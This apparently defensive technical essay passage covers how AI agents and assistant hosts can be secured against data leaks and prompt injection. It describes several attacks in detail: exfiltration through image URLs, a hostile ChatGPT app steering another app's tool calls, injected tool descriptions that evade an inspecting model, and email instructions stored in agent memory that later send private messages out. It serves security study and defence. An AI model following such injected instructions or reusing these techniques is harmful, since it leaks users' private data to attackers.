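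This check would have caught the image addresses in EchoLeak, ForcedLeak and the Superhuman attack. Each address contained text that the model had just taken from private data, so a crawler could not have recorded it, even on a trustworthy domain. Redirects also matter less, because a public address contains nothing about the user even if it leads to the attacker's site.

The method does not stop a model from choosing among addresses already in the index. Embrace The Red notes that OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges this, and that a larger website or blog probably already has the 36 indexed pages an attacker needs. Rehberger suggests preventing the agent from opening the same address twice in a session. That would slow down an attacker who has one address per character, but an attacker could avoid repeats by getting more pages indexed and using a separate set of addresses for each position,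 as in Radware's method.

Agents also have good reasons to open addresses that no crawler has seen. In the shopping task, Shop A's product pages are probably in the index, but the page with a delivery quote for this user probably isn't. The user would then get a warning about a step that the task requires. Checking addresses also doesn't cover text that the agent types into Shop A's delivery form, because a form can send its contents separately from the address. OpenAI promises only to stop the agent from quietly leaking data through the address itself.

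By March 2026, OpenAI had applied the mechanism to page visits in Atlas and to searches and page visits in Deep Research, its research agent, according to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026). But a company has to add such a check to every product that can fetch an address. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes an attack on Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, which an update had extended to tasks such as sorting email. An injection in one message made Codex display an image, and loading the image's address submitted other messages to a Google Form. PromptArmor reported the flaw on April 21, 2026, almost three months after OpenAI described its index, and disclosed it on May 21. OpenAI has since fixed it. An address containing a victim's mail could not have been in the index, so Codex was probably displaying images without the check. Rehberger had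 warned that some of OpenAI's developers might not know about the check or use it.

Chrome's agent follows a rule based on the same idea: it restricts addresses generated by the model to known public ones. Parker describes this rule as part of the control on page navigation and does not explain how Chrome determines that an address is public. If Chrome also uses a fixed set of addresses, an attacker could exploit the choice among them. Agent Origin Sets would make this harder, because the addresses would have to belong to sites that Chrome classifies as relevant to the task.

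### Displaying no remote images

In 2024, GitHub responded to a leak in Copilot Chat by blocking images from untrusted domains. CamoLeak later showed that images from a trusted domain could leak data too, and GitHub fixed it by turning off images in Copilot Chat. This is simpler than checking images against an index, and it prevents an attacker from leaking data through the choice of images to load. Losing images matters little in a coding assistant but more in a shopping assistant, whose users want to see the products.

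A host can instead ask the user before it loads an image. PromptArmor recommended that Notion, a note-taking application, do this for pages and email drafts that its AI writes. The host also has to apply the rule before the browser receives any part of the answer. SearchLeak succeeded because Copilot cleaned up the answer only at the end, after the browser had already received part of it.

An application that removes images can still leak data through links. Legit Security also got Copilot to put the encoded contents of a private project in a link, which would have leaked them if the user had clicked it. In some applications, no click is needed. Many people talk to agents such as OpenClaw through messaging applications, which fetch any link in a message to show a preview. PromptArmor found that this can leak data as soon as the agent's message arrives, and that OpenClaw used through Telegram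 was exposed by default. The agent's developers can't solve this by changing their interface, because another company's software displays the messages. They would have to turn off previews for the agent's messages or check each link before sending it.

### Network limits on code sandboxes

A CSP applies to pages in a browser, so it has no effect on a program that the model writes and runs in a sandbox. The operating system or the surrounding network has to enforce the limit there. The strongest rule is to allow no network access, and a program that only calculates averages from an uploaded spreadsheet doesn't need any. The ChatGPT case shows that the rule has to cover name lookups as well as connections.

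Other programs need to download software packages or call an outside service. A host can send their traffic through a proxy that runs outside the sandbox and holds the list of permitted sites. The proxy can also do the name lookups, and only for names on the list, so code in the sandbox can't send data to a name server by putting it in invented names. Listing exact names is safer than using wildcards, which would again allow invented subdomains.

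A proxy's list has the same weaknesses as a CSP's. If it permits a site where anyone can open an account and upload files, the code can upload the user's data to the attacker's account. A program can also make thousands of requests in a few seconds, so it could send a long document through a channel that carries only a few bits per request. The proxy can reduce this risk by permitting only downloads and limiting the number of requests. It can also keep copies of common packages, so that most requests never reach an outside server.

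OpenAI sandboxes the small applications that users run inside ChatGPT. The sandbox detects unexpected communication and prompts the user for consent.

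## Running third-party interfaces inside a chat

Outside companies supply some of the applications that run inside ChatGPT and other assistants. A shop, for example, can provide a product list that the user sorts and clicks without leaving the conversation. MCP Apps, the standard for such interfaces, lets an MCP server provide a web page that the host displays in the chat. Unlike SOPGuard and similar systems, which imitate browser mechanisms, the host uses the real ones: a sandboxed frame, a separate origin, a content security policy (CSP) and a permissions policy.

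### From proposal to official extension

Ido Salomon and Liad Yosef created an early system of this kind, MCP-UI. OpenAI launched its own, the Apps SDK, for ChatGPT in October 2025. The two used different conventions, so a developer who wanted to support several hosts had to maintain several versions of the same interface. On November 21, Salomon and Yosef joined developers from Anthropic and OpenAI in proposing a common standard, *SEP-1865* (Salomon, Yosef and colleagues, 2025).

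Model Context Protocol (2026) announced MCP Apps as the protocol's first official extension on January 26, 2026. Claude and the open-source agent Goose supported it that day, and ChatGPT began supporting it the same week. Agentic AI Foundation's *MCP Apps* (2026) reports that Cursor, GitHub Copilot and Postman also supported it by April. The protocol's July 28 revision includes MCP Apps as one of two official extensions, but the January specification is still the stable version. OpenAI's *Add UI to your MCP server* tells developers to build new interfaces on the shared standard and to use OpenAI's own functions only for extras such as checkout.

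### From a tool call to a page in the chat

Suppose Shop A runs an MCP server that can show its laptops in the chat:

1. When the host connects, the server lists its tools. The entry for the display tool includes the address of a template, a web page with scripts but no laptops in it yet.
2. The host fetches the template, either immediately or when it needs it. It can inspect the page before any of the code runs.
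3. The model calls the tool, and the host passes the call to the server.
4. The host loads the template in a sandboxed frame. Once the page reports that it is ready, the host sends it the tool's arguments and result, and the page fills in the laptops.
5. The user clicks a laptop. The page tells the host through postMessage, and the host decides what to do with the message.

MCP-UI returned the page inside the tool's result, which was more convenient for developers but gave the host nothing to review in advance. Even with a template, the host can't review the data that arrives in step 4, or future versions of any script that the template loads from elsewhere.

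### Why web hosts use two frames

A host that runs in a browser, such as ChatGPT's website, needs an origin for the app's page. Barthelet (2026), in *Why MCP and ChatGPT Apps Use Double Iframes*, goes through the simpler options and what goes wrong with each:

- If the host puts the template directly into an ordinary frame, the page shares the host's origin and inherits its CSP, which blocks the app's scripts. If the host relaxed the policy, those scripts could read what ChatGPT keeps in the browser's local storage.
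- A strict sandbox setting gives the page an origin that matches no other. This protects the host, but the app can no longer store anything in the browser.
- If the page comes from the developer's own server, it has a suitable origin, but the host has to add every developer's domain to its own policy.

The specification therefore requires web hosts to use an outer frame with a different origin from the chat. This frame holds a small loader page, which receives the template from the host and puts it in an inner frame. The host can serve the same loader from a different subdomain for each app, so the browser keeps each app's local storage separate.

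In *Confused ChatGPT*, Wang, Jha and Lin (2026) found this layout in ChatGPT. The same-origin policy separates the outer frame from the chat page, but not the app from the loader, because the app and loader share an origin. The host therefore has to make its security checks in the chat page, where the app's code can't alter them.

A server can request a dedicated origin for its app. Claude computes one from the server's address, so it stays the same across conversations and the developer's other services can recognise it. If the server doesn't request one, hosts will typically use one origin per conversation, according to the specification. Two apps in the same conversation could then share an origin, and the same-origin policy would not keep them apart. Separate subdomains are safer, but they can share cookies if an app sets a cookie's domain too broadly, and Chrome may treat them as one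 site and run them in the same process.

### Declared connections and device permissions

The server declares what its page needs in metadata that accompanies the template. Shop A's might look like this:

```json
"ui": {
  "csp": {
    "connectDomains": ["https://api.shop-a.example"],
    "resourceDomains": ["https://images.shop-a.example"]
  },
  "permissions": { "geolocation": {} },
  "domain": "shop-a.apps-host.example"
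}
```

| Field | What it controls | If the server omits it |
|---|---|---|
| `connectDomains` | Where the page's scripts may send requests | No outside connections |
| `resourceDomains` | Where outside images, scripts, styles, fonts and media may come from | No outside resources |
| `frameDomains` | Which origins the page may embed in frames of its own | No embedded frames |
| `permissions` | Use of the camera, microphone, location and clipboard (writing only) | No request for access |
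| `domain` | The dedicated origin, in a format that each host defines | The host's default origin |

The host turns the domain lists into a CSP. It may make the policy stricter, but it must not allow a domain that the server left out. It can pass the device requests on to the browser by listing the features the page may use in the frame's permissions policy. The host may refuse any of these requests, so Shop A's page has to work without the user's location.

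A CSP has a different role here than on an assistant's own page, because the app's developer writes the list of allowed domains. A dishonest developer can include their own server. That server also supplies the tool, so it already receives whatever the model puts in a call. The policy is more useful against third parties, such as a faulty advertising script that tries to contact an undeclared server. The host can also check the declared domains, and OpenAI's reviewers compare them with how the interface behaves.

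If a developer forgets to list a domain, the app breaks instead of exposing data. Barthelet has seen apps fail in production, or fail OpenAI's review, because a domain was missing. These failures give developers a reason to fix the list, whereas a forgotten label in SPIDES could go unnoticed.

The domain lists don't cover links that the app asks the host to open, so data can still leave in a link's address. Under the specification, hosts should open these links but may refuse. Wang, Jha and Lin found that the request brings up a link safety check in ChatGPT.

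### Why the browser's limits work here

These mechanisms transfer well because an app's page is ordinary web code, and nothing it displays can change the browser's origin checks or the CSP. A browser engine is far too large for the complete analysis Anderson requires, but browser makers have long experience confining hostile pages, and a single fix to the engine protects every app.

The messages between the page and the host are also easy to check with ordinary code, because each has a fixed format and specifies the operation it requests. For example, a page may call tools only on the server it came from, and the host must reject a call to any tool that the server hasn't made available to apps. Shop A's page therefore cannot search the user's mailbox through the mail server, whatever code its developer writes.

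### How an app's words reach the model

The model can search the mailbox, though, and the page can send text to the model. Apps have good reasons to send this text. If the user clicks a laptop and then types "is this one light enough to travel with?", the model needs the page to identify the laptop. The page can either add a message to the chat, which prompts the model to respond, or update the context for later turns without starting a response.

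The frame doesn't restrict what an app's text says, so a malicious app can include an instruction, and a benign one can pass on an instruction from a customer's review.

| What the page requests | Required of the host | Recommended | Optional |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call a tool on its own server | Reject the call if the tool is not available to apps | – | Ask the user first |
| Add a message to the chat | – | Add it in the role the page gives, which is the user's | Ask the user first |
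| Update the model's context | – | Give the model the latest update in future turns | Show the update to the user |

The second row is the most troubling because the specification recommends adding the app's text to the conversation as a user message, and models learn to give user messages more weight than tool output. The host can identify which frame sent the message, so its code could label the text with the app's origin, as SOPGuard does for web pages, without relying on a model to determine the source.

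Context updates can be harder to notice. According to the January announcement, apps can "quietly update the model's context", and hosts need not display these updates. Model Context Protocol's notes on the July revision state that actions from an app's interface follow "the same audit and consent path as a direct tool call", but the specification lets each host decide whether that path includes an approval.

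### Tests on ChatGPT apps

Wang, Jha and Lin tested whether one ChatGPT app could use this channel to influence another. ChatGPT's app directory had grown from 122 apps in December 2025 to 888 by early May 2026. The researchers wrote two apps, a hostile one that finds tourist attractions and a harmless one that searches for hotels. They ran both in their own accounts without publishing them.

In the first attack, the user asked for viewpoints in Tokyo. The hostile app returned a genuine list, but its page also sent the model a message on how to handle hotel requests. When the user later asked for hotels, the model had the hotel app search in Osaka instead of Tokyo. The hotel app worked correctly throughout, so a user who noticed the mistake would probably blame that app or the model. In the second attack, the message made the model call the hotel app immediately, without any request from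 the user.

The browser enforced all its limits during these attacks. The hostile page got the model to call the hotel app's tool, without touching the app's page or calling the tool itself. This makes the model a confused deputy, like Hardy's compiler.

Both attacks worked on all six models tested, from o3 to GPT 5.5 Thinking. GPT 5.2 Thinking treated the app's message as the user's own, so the researchers reworded the text for that model. They don't report how often each attack succeeded, so the results don't show how reliable the attacks are. The hotel app could only search, and a tool that spends money might have triggered a request for approval.

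The attacks used a documented ChatGPT function, which OpenAI lists as the equivalent of the standard's chat message. Wang, Jha and Lin also found two undocumented options for this function. One gave the app's text the same priority as the platform's own instructions, and the other hid the message from the user. None of the apps whose code they could analyse used either option.

The researchers reported this to OpenAI on March 9, 2026. OpenAI judged the report out of scope for its bounty program, which treats prompt injection as model behaviour rather than a platform vulnerability. The undocumented options still worked in May.

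Reviewing apps before publication may not catch such an attack. Some apps compose their messages while they run, often from text that the developer's server sends, and the developer can change that text after the review. Banning the function would also break useful apps. The researchers found it in 75 of them, including a language course that asks the model for a practice sentence after each quiz. Even with a ban, apps would have other ways to influence the model. A tool's description also affected the behaviour of GPT 5.5 Thinking, though the model resisted instructions placed in a tool's results.

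### Narrowing the channel

Wang, Jha and Lin recommend removing the undocumented options immediately. They also suggest that ChatGPT show every message from an app under that app's name, and ask the user before the model calls one app's tool just after another app has added to the context. The last rule would have interrupted the second attack. It might have missed the first, in which the hostile text could take effect several turns later, and it would interrupt many legitimate tasks that combine apps.

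For the longer term, Wang, Jha and Lin propose giving each app a separate context and having the host check what returns to the main conversation. They argue that even this can't give a firm guarantee, because an app returns ordinary language and only another model can judge what it means. Their argument holds for free text, but the dual-model pattern avoids the problem by returning only values that code can check. Wang, Jha and Lin's suggestion that apps declare the purpose of the data they share comes close to this.

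Such a restriction limits the user less with MCP Apps than in a text-only chat, because the user can read Shop A's descriptions and reviews in the frame without the model receiving them. When the user clicks a laptop, the host could accept only an item number from the page. The model would then have the user's choice, but it couldn't answer a question about the reviews.

The current standard doesn't enforce this separation. It lets an app put any text in a context update, and hosts differ in what they give the model from a tool's result. Salomon and colleagues describe one field of the result as data for the interface that stays out of the model's context. But in ChatGPT the model receives that field too, so a developer who puts customer reviews there for display also gives them to the model.

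## Permissions for tools that web pages and servers offer

A host that displays MCP Apps can use the browser's permissions policy to control whether an app's page may use the camera or the user's location. Ordinary websites can now offer tools to agents through a proposed standard called WebMCP, and the same policy controls which pages may do so. But browsers' other permission checks rely on a person looking at the page, and there may be no one looking when an agent is using it.

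### How browsers control sensitive features

Suppose Shop A's page contains a map from another company in a frame, and the map requests the user's location. The browser checks the permissions policy first. Browsers turn location off by default in frames from other origins, so the browser rejects the request without prompting the user unless the shop has added `allow="geolocation"` to the frame. If the policy allows the request, the browser shows a permission prompt and usually remembers the user's answer for that site.

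Other features, such as pop-up windows and full-screen display, require user activation, meaning they work only shortly after a real click, tap or key press on the page. The activation expires within seconds, and opening a pop-up uses it up, so one click can't open several. Scripts can simulate clicks on their own page, but the browser doesn't count these as activation.

| Mechanism | Who decides | What it assumes about the user |
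|---|---|---|
| Permissions policy | The page's developer | Nothing, so it works even if nobody is present |
| Permission prompt | The user | Someone is present, reads the question and understands it |
| User activation | The browser, from mouse, touch or keyboard input | Someone chose to interact with the page |

### How a page registers a tool

With WebMCP, a page describes its functions to the agent, so the agent doesn't have to work out what each button does. Shop A could register a tool for delivery quotes:

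```js
document.modelContext.registerTool({
  name: "get_delivery_quote",
  description: "Returns the delivery cost for an address",
  inputSchema: quoteInputs,
  annotations: { readOnlyHint: true },
  execute: getQuote
}, {
  exposedTo: ["https://compare.example"]
});
```

The agent reads the tool's name, description and list of inputs, and calls it with an address. The browser then runs the shop's `getQuote` function in the open page and returns the result to the agent. Unlike an MCP server, which is a separate program, this function runs inside the page, where the user may be logged in.

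A site can also turn an existing form into a tool by adding a few attributes to its HTML. The example in InfoQ (2026) includes `toolautosubmit`, which lets the agent submit the form. Without that attribute, the agent fills in the form and the user submits it.

### What the browser enforces and what the site declares

Chrome for Developers (2026) describes a permissions policy named `tools`, which by default lets only the page and frames from its own origin register tools. A frame from another origin can register tools only if the embedding page grants it `allow="tools"`.

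The August 2026 version of Chrome for Developers also requires origin isolation. An old browser feature, `document.domain`, lets pages on different subdomains agree to act as one origin. Chrome disables WebMCP on pages that keep this feature available, so that a tool's origin can't change while the tool exists.

In the May 2026 draft of the Web Machine Learning Community Group's *WebMCP*, a page can see a tool if the page has the same origin as the tool's owner or if its origin is on the tool's `exposedTo` list. This rule also covers agents that websites build into their own pages, but not the browser's own agent, which in the draft's example receives the tools from every frame in the tab. Under the draft, browsers should pass on each tool's origin so that the model can tell the parties apart.

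A site can also attach hints to its tools, which Chrome for Developers explains in its security advice.

| Setting | Purpose | Enforced by the browser? |
|---|---|---|
| `tools` policy | Controls which pages and frames may register tools | Yes |
| Origin isolation | Keeps a tool's origin fixed | Yes |
| `exposedTo` | Controls which other origins can see and call a tool | Yes |
| `untrustedContentHint` | Warns that the output may contain other people's text | No |
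| `readOnlyHint` | Declares that the tool changes nothing | No |
| `consequentialHint` | Declares that the action is significant or hard to reverse | No |

The hints help when the site is honest. A hostile site can label a tool read-only even though it places an order, and an agent that relies on the hint might run it without asking the user first. Google advises agent developers to assume that a tool changes something unless the site clearly states otherwise. This protects the user when a site omits the hint, but not when the hint is false.

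The draft's default for untrusted content is less cautious. If Shop A forgets to add the hint to a tool that returns customer reviews, the browser records the output as not untrusted. Google's sample instructions for agents treat all WebMCP output as untrusted, so they don't depend on the site to add the hint, but they work only if the model follows them.

The browser also doesn't check whether a tool needs the information it requests. In *Privacy and security considerations for WebMCP*, Huang (2025) of Microsoft gives the example of a dress search that asks for the user's age, location and whether they are pregnant, as well as their size. An agent that knows these details may supply them all. Huang also points out that a tool named `finalizeCart` might either show the cart or complete the purchase.

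### The debate over embedded pages

Browser developers and other companies discuss WebMCP in a community group at W3C, the web standards organisation. On April 16, 2026, the group debated which tools a page in a frame should expose by default. The minutes, W3C's *WebML CG Teleconference* (2026), record that Johann Hofmann of Google wanted such tools hidden from both the surrounding page and the agent until the site opted in.

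Hofmann worried about a bank whose page offers a tool for making transfers. An attacker could embed that page in a hostile one and use a prompt injection to persuade the agent to call the tool. The hostile page wouldn't need access to the tool itself. Hofmann considered this close to a violation of the same-origin policy.

Dominic Farolino, also of Google, replied that an agent is an extension of the user, and that an attacker could already trick a person into clicking the same things. Farolino hoped that sites with sensitive tools would be careful about who could embed them. Benjamin VanderSloot of Mozilla expected developers to copy unsafe settings from code examples online. Yoav Weiss suggested exposing tools to agents but not to other origins.

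The group agreed to combine the `exposedTo` list with the permissions policy, and the May draft follows Weiss's suggestion. Neither mechanism prevents Hofmann's attack, because the attacker controls the outer page and can add `allow="tools"` to the bank's frame. The agent sees the bank's tool even if `exposedTo` is empty. The bank can protect itself by refusing to appear in other sites' frames.

Hofmann also described the reverse danger, in which an embedded page first offers a useful tool and later uses it to send the agent hostile text. The surrounding page can withhold permission for tools, but the embedded page sets the `exposedTo` list.

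### Where the proposal stands

WebMCP is still an experiment. The Web Machine Learning Community Group states on the draft that it is neither a W3C standard nor on the standards track. Chrome offers it from version 149 in an origin trial, which lets participating sites test an unfinished feature with real users. Edge also has a trial, which Microsoft's *WebMCP* lists as ending on November 17, 2026.

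When Google announced developer testing of WebMCP in February, *Ready for Developer Testing* (Chromestatus, 2026) recorded no position from the developers of Firefox's or Safari's engine. By late June, Apple had suggested moving WebMCP out of the community group, and VanderSloot said Mozilla had no strong opinion. According to W3C's minutes of June 25, the group was preparing to transfer it to a working group, which can produce formal standards.

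The group also requested architecture, privacy and security reviews, but none had produced an official response by August 20. W3C's minutes from that day mention a draft threat model. At that meeting, Farolino said that security was one of the main sticking points, and that people new to WebMCP confuse it with other issues, such as agents mixing data from several tabs.

### Scripts that share an origin

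The `tools` policy and the `exposedTo` list distinguish only between origins, so neither separates an advertiser's script from the shop's own code on the same page. This matches the browser's general design. Chromium's *Web Platform Security guidelines* name the origin as the boundary the project aims to defend.

In tests by Lee and colleagues in August 2026, a hostile script removed or replaced another script's tools in all 20 attempts when there was no added defence. Their system, WebMCP-Phalanx, gives each tool's credential only to the script that registered it, and with it in place none of the 20 attempts succeeded. A script that loads early can still take a name such as `checkout` before the shop's code registers it.

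Lee and colleagues built the system in JavaScript on top of a reference version of WebMCP. A version built into the browser would be harder to tamper with. To distinguish the shop's scripts from an advertiser's, they recommend that the browser record which script registered each tool and that sites declare which scripts they trust, much as sites do in a content security policy.

A hostile script can also register a tool whose description or output contains an injection. WebMCP-Phalanx therefore has a quarantined model inspect this text before the model that calls tools reads it. The table shows how many of 80 attacks succeeded.

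| Defence | Injection in the description | Injection in the output |
|---|---|---|
| None | 69 | 42 |
| Trust labels only | 71 | 38 |
| Removing the text without reading it | 25 | 2 |
| Inspection by a quarantined model | 0 | 2 |

The labels helped little because the hostile tool had a valid credential and so appeared trustworthy. The inspection worked much better, but in two cases the agent called a tool before the inspection could block it, because the tool's name suited the task.

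An adaptive attacker who knew the inspecting model's instructions got past it with 15 of 16 attacks on descriptions, usually after a single rewrite. These attacks moved the persuasive part into the tool's name, which the inspection didn't cover. Lee and colleagues proposed delaying every call until the host has checked the names as well, but did not test this.

Removing a tool also leaves its earlier output in the agent's context. In another test, one page's tool returned instructions for a bank transfer, and the agent then moved to a second page. Deleting the first page's tool reduced the attack's success rate only from 80% to 70%. When the system also stopped treating the old output as trusted, the rate fell to zero.

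### Declared permissions for MCP servers

An MCP server on the user's computer often runs with all the user's privileges, so a weather tool may be able to read private files. *Securing AI Agent Execution* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) describes AgentBound, which was built to restrict such servers the way Android restricts applications.

Each server comes with a manifest, a file that lists the kinds of access it needs, such as reading files or contacting other computers. In the laptop-shopping task, a notes server that stores its files locally might work like this:

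1. The manifest requests permission to read and write files, but not to use the network.
2. When the host starts the server, the user chooses the folder to which these permissions apply.
3. AgentBound runs the server in a container, an isolated environment that holds only that folder.
4. If the host tries to grant network access, AgentBound stops, because the manifest doesn't include it.

The second step provides much of the protection. Among 296 popular servers, 83.1% needed outgoing network access and 74.1% needed to read files, so a manifest with both permissions doesn't make a server unusual. Restricting a server to a particular folder and web address limits what it can steal.

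Bühler and colleagues used language models to write the manifests from the servers' code, and report an accuracy of 80.9%. They asked the developers of 96 servers to check the results, but 74% didn't respond, so this figure is based on only about 17 who accepted the manifest and four who rejected it. In a more informative check, two of the researchers wrote manifests for 48 servers by hand, and the generated ones agreed with 96.4% of their decisions. Most of the errors were missing permissions, which would stop a server from working properly but wouldn't give it too much access.

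In tests with malicious servers, AgentBound blocked all nine attacks that tried to misuse files, the network or other system resources, including one by a maps server that secretly switched to an attacker's address. AgentBound missed an attack in which a clock server's description told the model to redirect cryptocurrency transfers made with a wallet server's tool. The clock server needed no extra access, and the wallet server contacted only a network address it was allowed to use. As with ChatGPT apps, the attack went through the model, which AgentBound doesn't control.

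### When an agent clicks for the user

User activation is weak evidence of what a person wants, since a page can trick people into clicking, but it normally shows that someone touched the mouse, screen or keyboard. An agent that sends clicks through the browser's own input system can produce the same signal with nobody at the computer. If a hostile review leads the agent to click, the page may be able to open a pop-up or use another feature that is supposed to require a human action.

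Permission prompts are harder for an agent to answer because the browser displays them outside the page, but an agent that controls the whole desktop may still be able to click "Allow". The user's earlier answers also still apply, so if the user once let Shop A read their location, the shop may be able to read it again when the agent visits.

WebMCP replaces some clicks with direct calls to a page's functions. The May draft doesn't require user activation for these calls or specify whether a call counts as activation. It includes a function that lets a tool request the user's input partway through a call, for instance to confirm an order.

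This works poorly if the browser runs on a remote server and the user is typing in a chat application, because the page's dialog appears where nobody will see it. According to W3C's minutes, the group agreed on June 11 to begin with a revised version for dialogs within the page. It left two other methods open. One would send the user a web address where they could enter sensitive details without passing them through the agent.

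A site can also abuse requests for attention. In W3C's minutes of May 14, VanderSloot warned of a site "hammering away" at the user. An earlier discussion, recorded in W3C's *WebML CG Teleconference* (2025), covered the related problems that the site and the agent might both ask about the same action and that a malicious site's wording might look official in the browser's own dialog.

### Chrome's confirmations

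Chrome's agent asks for confirmation in three situations, as Parker described them in December 2025:

| Situation | How Chrome recognises it |
|---|---|
| Opening a sensitive site, such as a bank or a medical site | Code compares the address with a list |
| Signing in with a saved password | The sign-in goes through Google Password Manager |
| Buying something, sending a message or taking another consequential action | The agent tries to recognise the action and pause |

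The first two don't depend on a model detecting that an action is risky. The third is less certain, and Parker promises only that the agent "will try to pause". For some of these actions, Chrome prompts the user to take the final step, such as clicking the payment button, which restores a real human click at the most important point. Chrome also shows a log of the agent's work, and the user can pause the agent or take over at any time.

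Entering a private message in Shop A's delivery form doesn't involve a sensitive site, a sign-in or a purchase, so Chrome would ask the user about it only if the agent recognised the entry as consequential.

### Habitual approval

Studies of older permission systems suggest that people may not read such requests carefully. Felt and colleagues (2012), in *Android Permissions*, studied the list that Android then showed users before they installed an application. Only 17% of participants paid attention to it, and 3% of the people surveyed correctly answered all three questions about what permissions meant. AgentBound's manifests borrow from the same system, but AgentBound also asks the user to choose specific folders and addresses.

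But people don't ignore every warning. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) analysed more than 25 million browser warnings. Users clicked through 70.2% of Chrome's warnings about a site's encryption and about a third of Firefox's. They clicked through no more than about a quarter of either browser's malware and phishing warnings. The warnings' design and frequency may explain part of the difference.

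These studies don't show how often people would approve an agent's harmful action, and security tests of agent hosts rarely measure it. Zverev and colleagues simulated a user who recognises every attack, and Bühler and colleagues had a single tester give consent. AgentBound has to prompt users for permission again whenever a server needs a different folder, so they would see many harmless requests.

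## Partitioned storage as a model for agent memory

Many agent hosts save information from one task and give it to the model in later ones, so data can pass between sites that the user visits weeks apart. Browsers had a similar problem with cookies, which let an advertising company recognise the same person on every site that displayed its content. Browser makers responded by storing the company's data separately for each site.

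### Tracking through a shared cookie

Suppose Shop A and a clinic both display images from an advertising company at `ads.example`. When the user opens Shop A, the browser requests an image, and the company's server replies with a cookie containing an identifier. When the user later opens the clinic's site, the browser requests another image from `ads.example` and attaches the same cookie. The company now knows that one person visited both sites.

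WebKit, the project behind Safari's browser engine, points out that a third-party cookie is an ordinary cookie that the browser sends or accepts when a page from one site loads content from another. The same-origin policy doesn't prevent companies from tracking users with these cookies, because each company reads only its own cookie.

State partitioning adds the site the user is visiting to the key that the browser uses to look up stored data. Mozilla's *State Partitioning* calls this double-keying. The key is now a pair, made up of the top-level site (the one in the address bar) and the origin of the embedded content:

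| The user visits | Key for the company's data | Identifier the company finds |
|---|---|---|
| Shop A | (`https://shop-a.example`, `https://ads.example`) | 4711 |
| The clinic | (`https://clinic.example`, `https://ads.example`) | 8032 |
| The company's own site | (`https://ads.example`, `https://ads.example`) | 1560 |

The company can still store data on each site, but the identifiers no longer match. Firefox also partitions its caches and network connections, which trackers can misuse in the same way. As a result, it may have to download the same file once for each site.

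Even with partitioned storage, one site can pass an identifier to another in a link's URL. When Safari detects this, it limits cookies that scripts create on the destination page to 24 hours.

### What browsers partition today

| Browser | Third-party cookies | Other third-party storage |
|---|---|---|
| Firefox | Partitions them by default since version 103 | Partitions it by default since version 103 |
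| Safari | Blocks them by default | Partitions it and deletes it when the user quits |
| Chrome | Allows them unless the user blocks them | Partitions it since version 115 |

Chrome's partitioning, described in Google's *Storage Partitioning*, therefore does not fully prevent tracking. With the default settings, `ads.example` can still recognise a Chrome user by an ordinary cookie. According to the UK's competition regulator, the CMA, Google had planned to remove third-party cookies but confirmed in April 2025 that it would not.

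Sites can also ask the browser to partition their cookies. Google's *Cookies Having Independent Partitioned State (CHIPS)* gives the example of a shop that embeds another company's support chat. The chat company marks its cookie as partitioned, and the browser then returns that cookie only when the chat appears on the same shop's site. Google made this optional because some services break if a browser partitions their cookies without warning. Safari had tried automatic partitioning and abandoned it, partly because it confused developers. Safari 26.2 brought partitioned cookies back, "this time opt-in", according to WebKit. Chavez (2025) confirmed in *Update on Plans for Privacy Sandbox Technologies* that Google still supports them in Chrome, though it is retiring many related features.

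### The Storage Access API

Some embedded content needs its usual cookies. For example, a video service may want to hide advertisements from subscribers who watch its videos on a news site. Google's *Storage Access API* explains how the service can request an exception:

1. The user clicks something in the video frame, and the frame's script requests access.
2. The browser checks that the user has previously visited the video service directly and interacted with it. If not, it refuses without showing a prompt.
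3. In most cases, the browser asks the user for permission.
4. If the user agrees, the frame receives the same cookies it would have on the service's own site.

Chrome and Firefox can renew the access on later visits without another click, while Safari always requires one. Firefox skips the prompt for the first five requests from a site the user knows. It also grants some exceptions automatically, such as 30 days of access for a service that opens a pop-up window in which the user clicks or types. Mozilla describes these automatic exceptions as temporary measures to keep existing sites working.

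### What agents remember

Agent memory is any information that a host saves from one conversation and adds to the context of a later one. Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2026), in *Trojan Hippo Bench*, tested four common forms:

| Form | What the host saves | What returns to the context |
|---|---|---|
| Full history | The whole conversation, except the oldest parts once space runs out | Everything saved |
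| Searchable history | The conversation, in pieces of 512 characters | The eight pieces that best match the user's message |
| Explicit list | Facts the model records when asked to remember something | The whole list |
| Extracted facts | Short facts that a second model takes from each exchange | The ten most relevant facts |

Users may not know what a host has saved. *Always-On Agents* (2026) cites an audit of 2,050 real memory entries, 96% of which the system had created silently and without the user's authorisation.

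Existing products partition memory mainly by user. According to *Isolated but Exposed* (2026), ChatGPT and Claude tie each memory to one user's account. Mem0, a widely used memory system for agents, can also separate entries by agent, session and application, using filters on a shared database. An account boundary stops one user from reading another's memories, but it doesn't separate what the agent learned at Shop A from what it learned at the clinic.

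### History carried between websites

In tests in early 2026, Roesner and Kohlbrenner asked agentic browsers what they knew about Alice from past browsing and chats. ChatGPT Atlas (in both modes), Chrome with Gemini and Perplexity Comet used chat history from other tabs, at least sometimes. Near the end of the tests, Comet correctly listed seven animals from pages the researchers had visited. Brave Leo, Copilot and Firefox saved their chats but did not use them in other tabs. Claude for Chrome did not appear to save its chats to the user's account.

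The researchers also describe an attack that needs no prompt injection. A user visits a phishing page that imitates their bank's website and lists a false phone number. The agent might recognise the page as fraudulent, but the number could remain in its history. When the user later asks for the bank's number, the agent might give the false one, having lost track of where it came from. Roesner and Kohlbrenner did not test this case, but they found that Atlas confused the contents of named tabs with pages it had visited earlier, which makes such a mistake plausible.

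Training a model to ignore hostile instructions would not prevent this attack, because the page contains only a false fact.

### Instructions that wait in memory

Das and colleagues tested an injection attack in which the attacker emails the user, and the host saves the email's text when the agent reads the mailbox. The injection has no effect until the user mentions a sensitive subject, such as their health or taxes. The agent then emails the user's message to the attacker.

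Hosts often place recalled memories among their own standing instructions, which models learn to trust more than a tool's output. With Gemini 3.1 Pro and no defence, the attack succeeded in 80% to 100% of runs, depending on the form of memory, even after 100 harmless sessions. The researchers then tried four defences:

| Defence | Attack success, all forms of memory | Average task success, searchable history |
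|---|---|---|
| None | 80–100% | 99% |
| Save only the user's own messages | 5–10% | 89% |
| Save nothing more in a session once the agent has read mail | 0–5% | 71% |
| Limit each entry to 80 characters | 20–85% | 89% |
| Label entries from mail, and block sending once one returns | 0% | 71% |

The averages don't show that, with the defences in the third and fifth rows, at least one of the seven kinds of harmless task never succeeded. In the laptop-shopping task, the third row's defence would discard the finished price comparison if the agent had already read the mail. With labels, the agent could save the delivery address but could not send anything in a later session that recalled the address.

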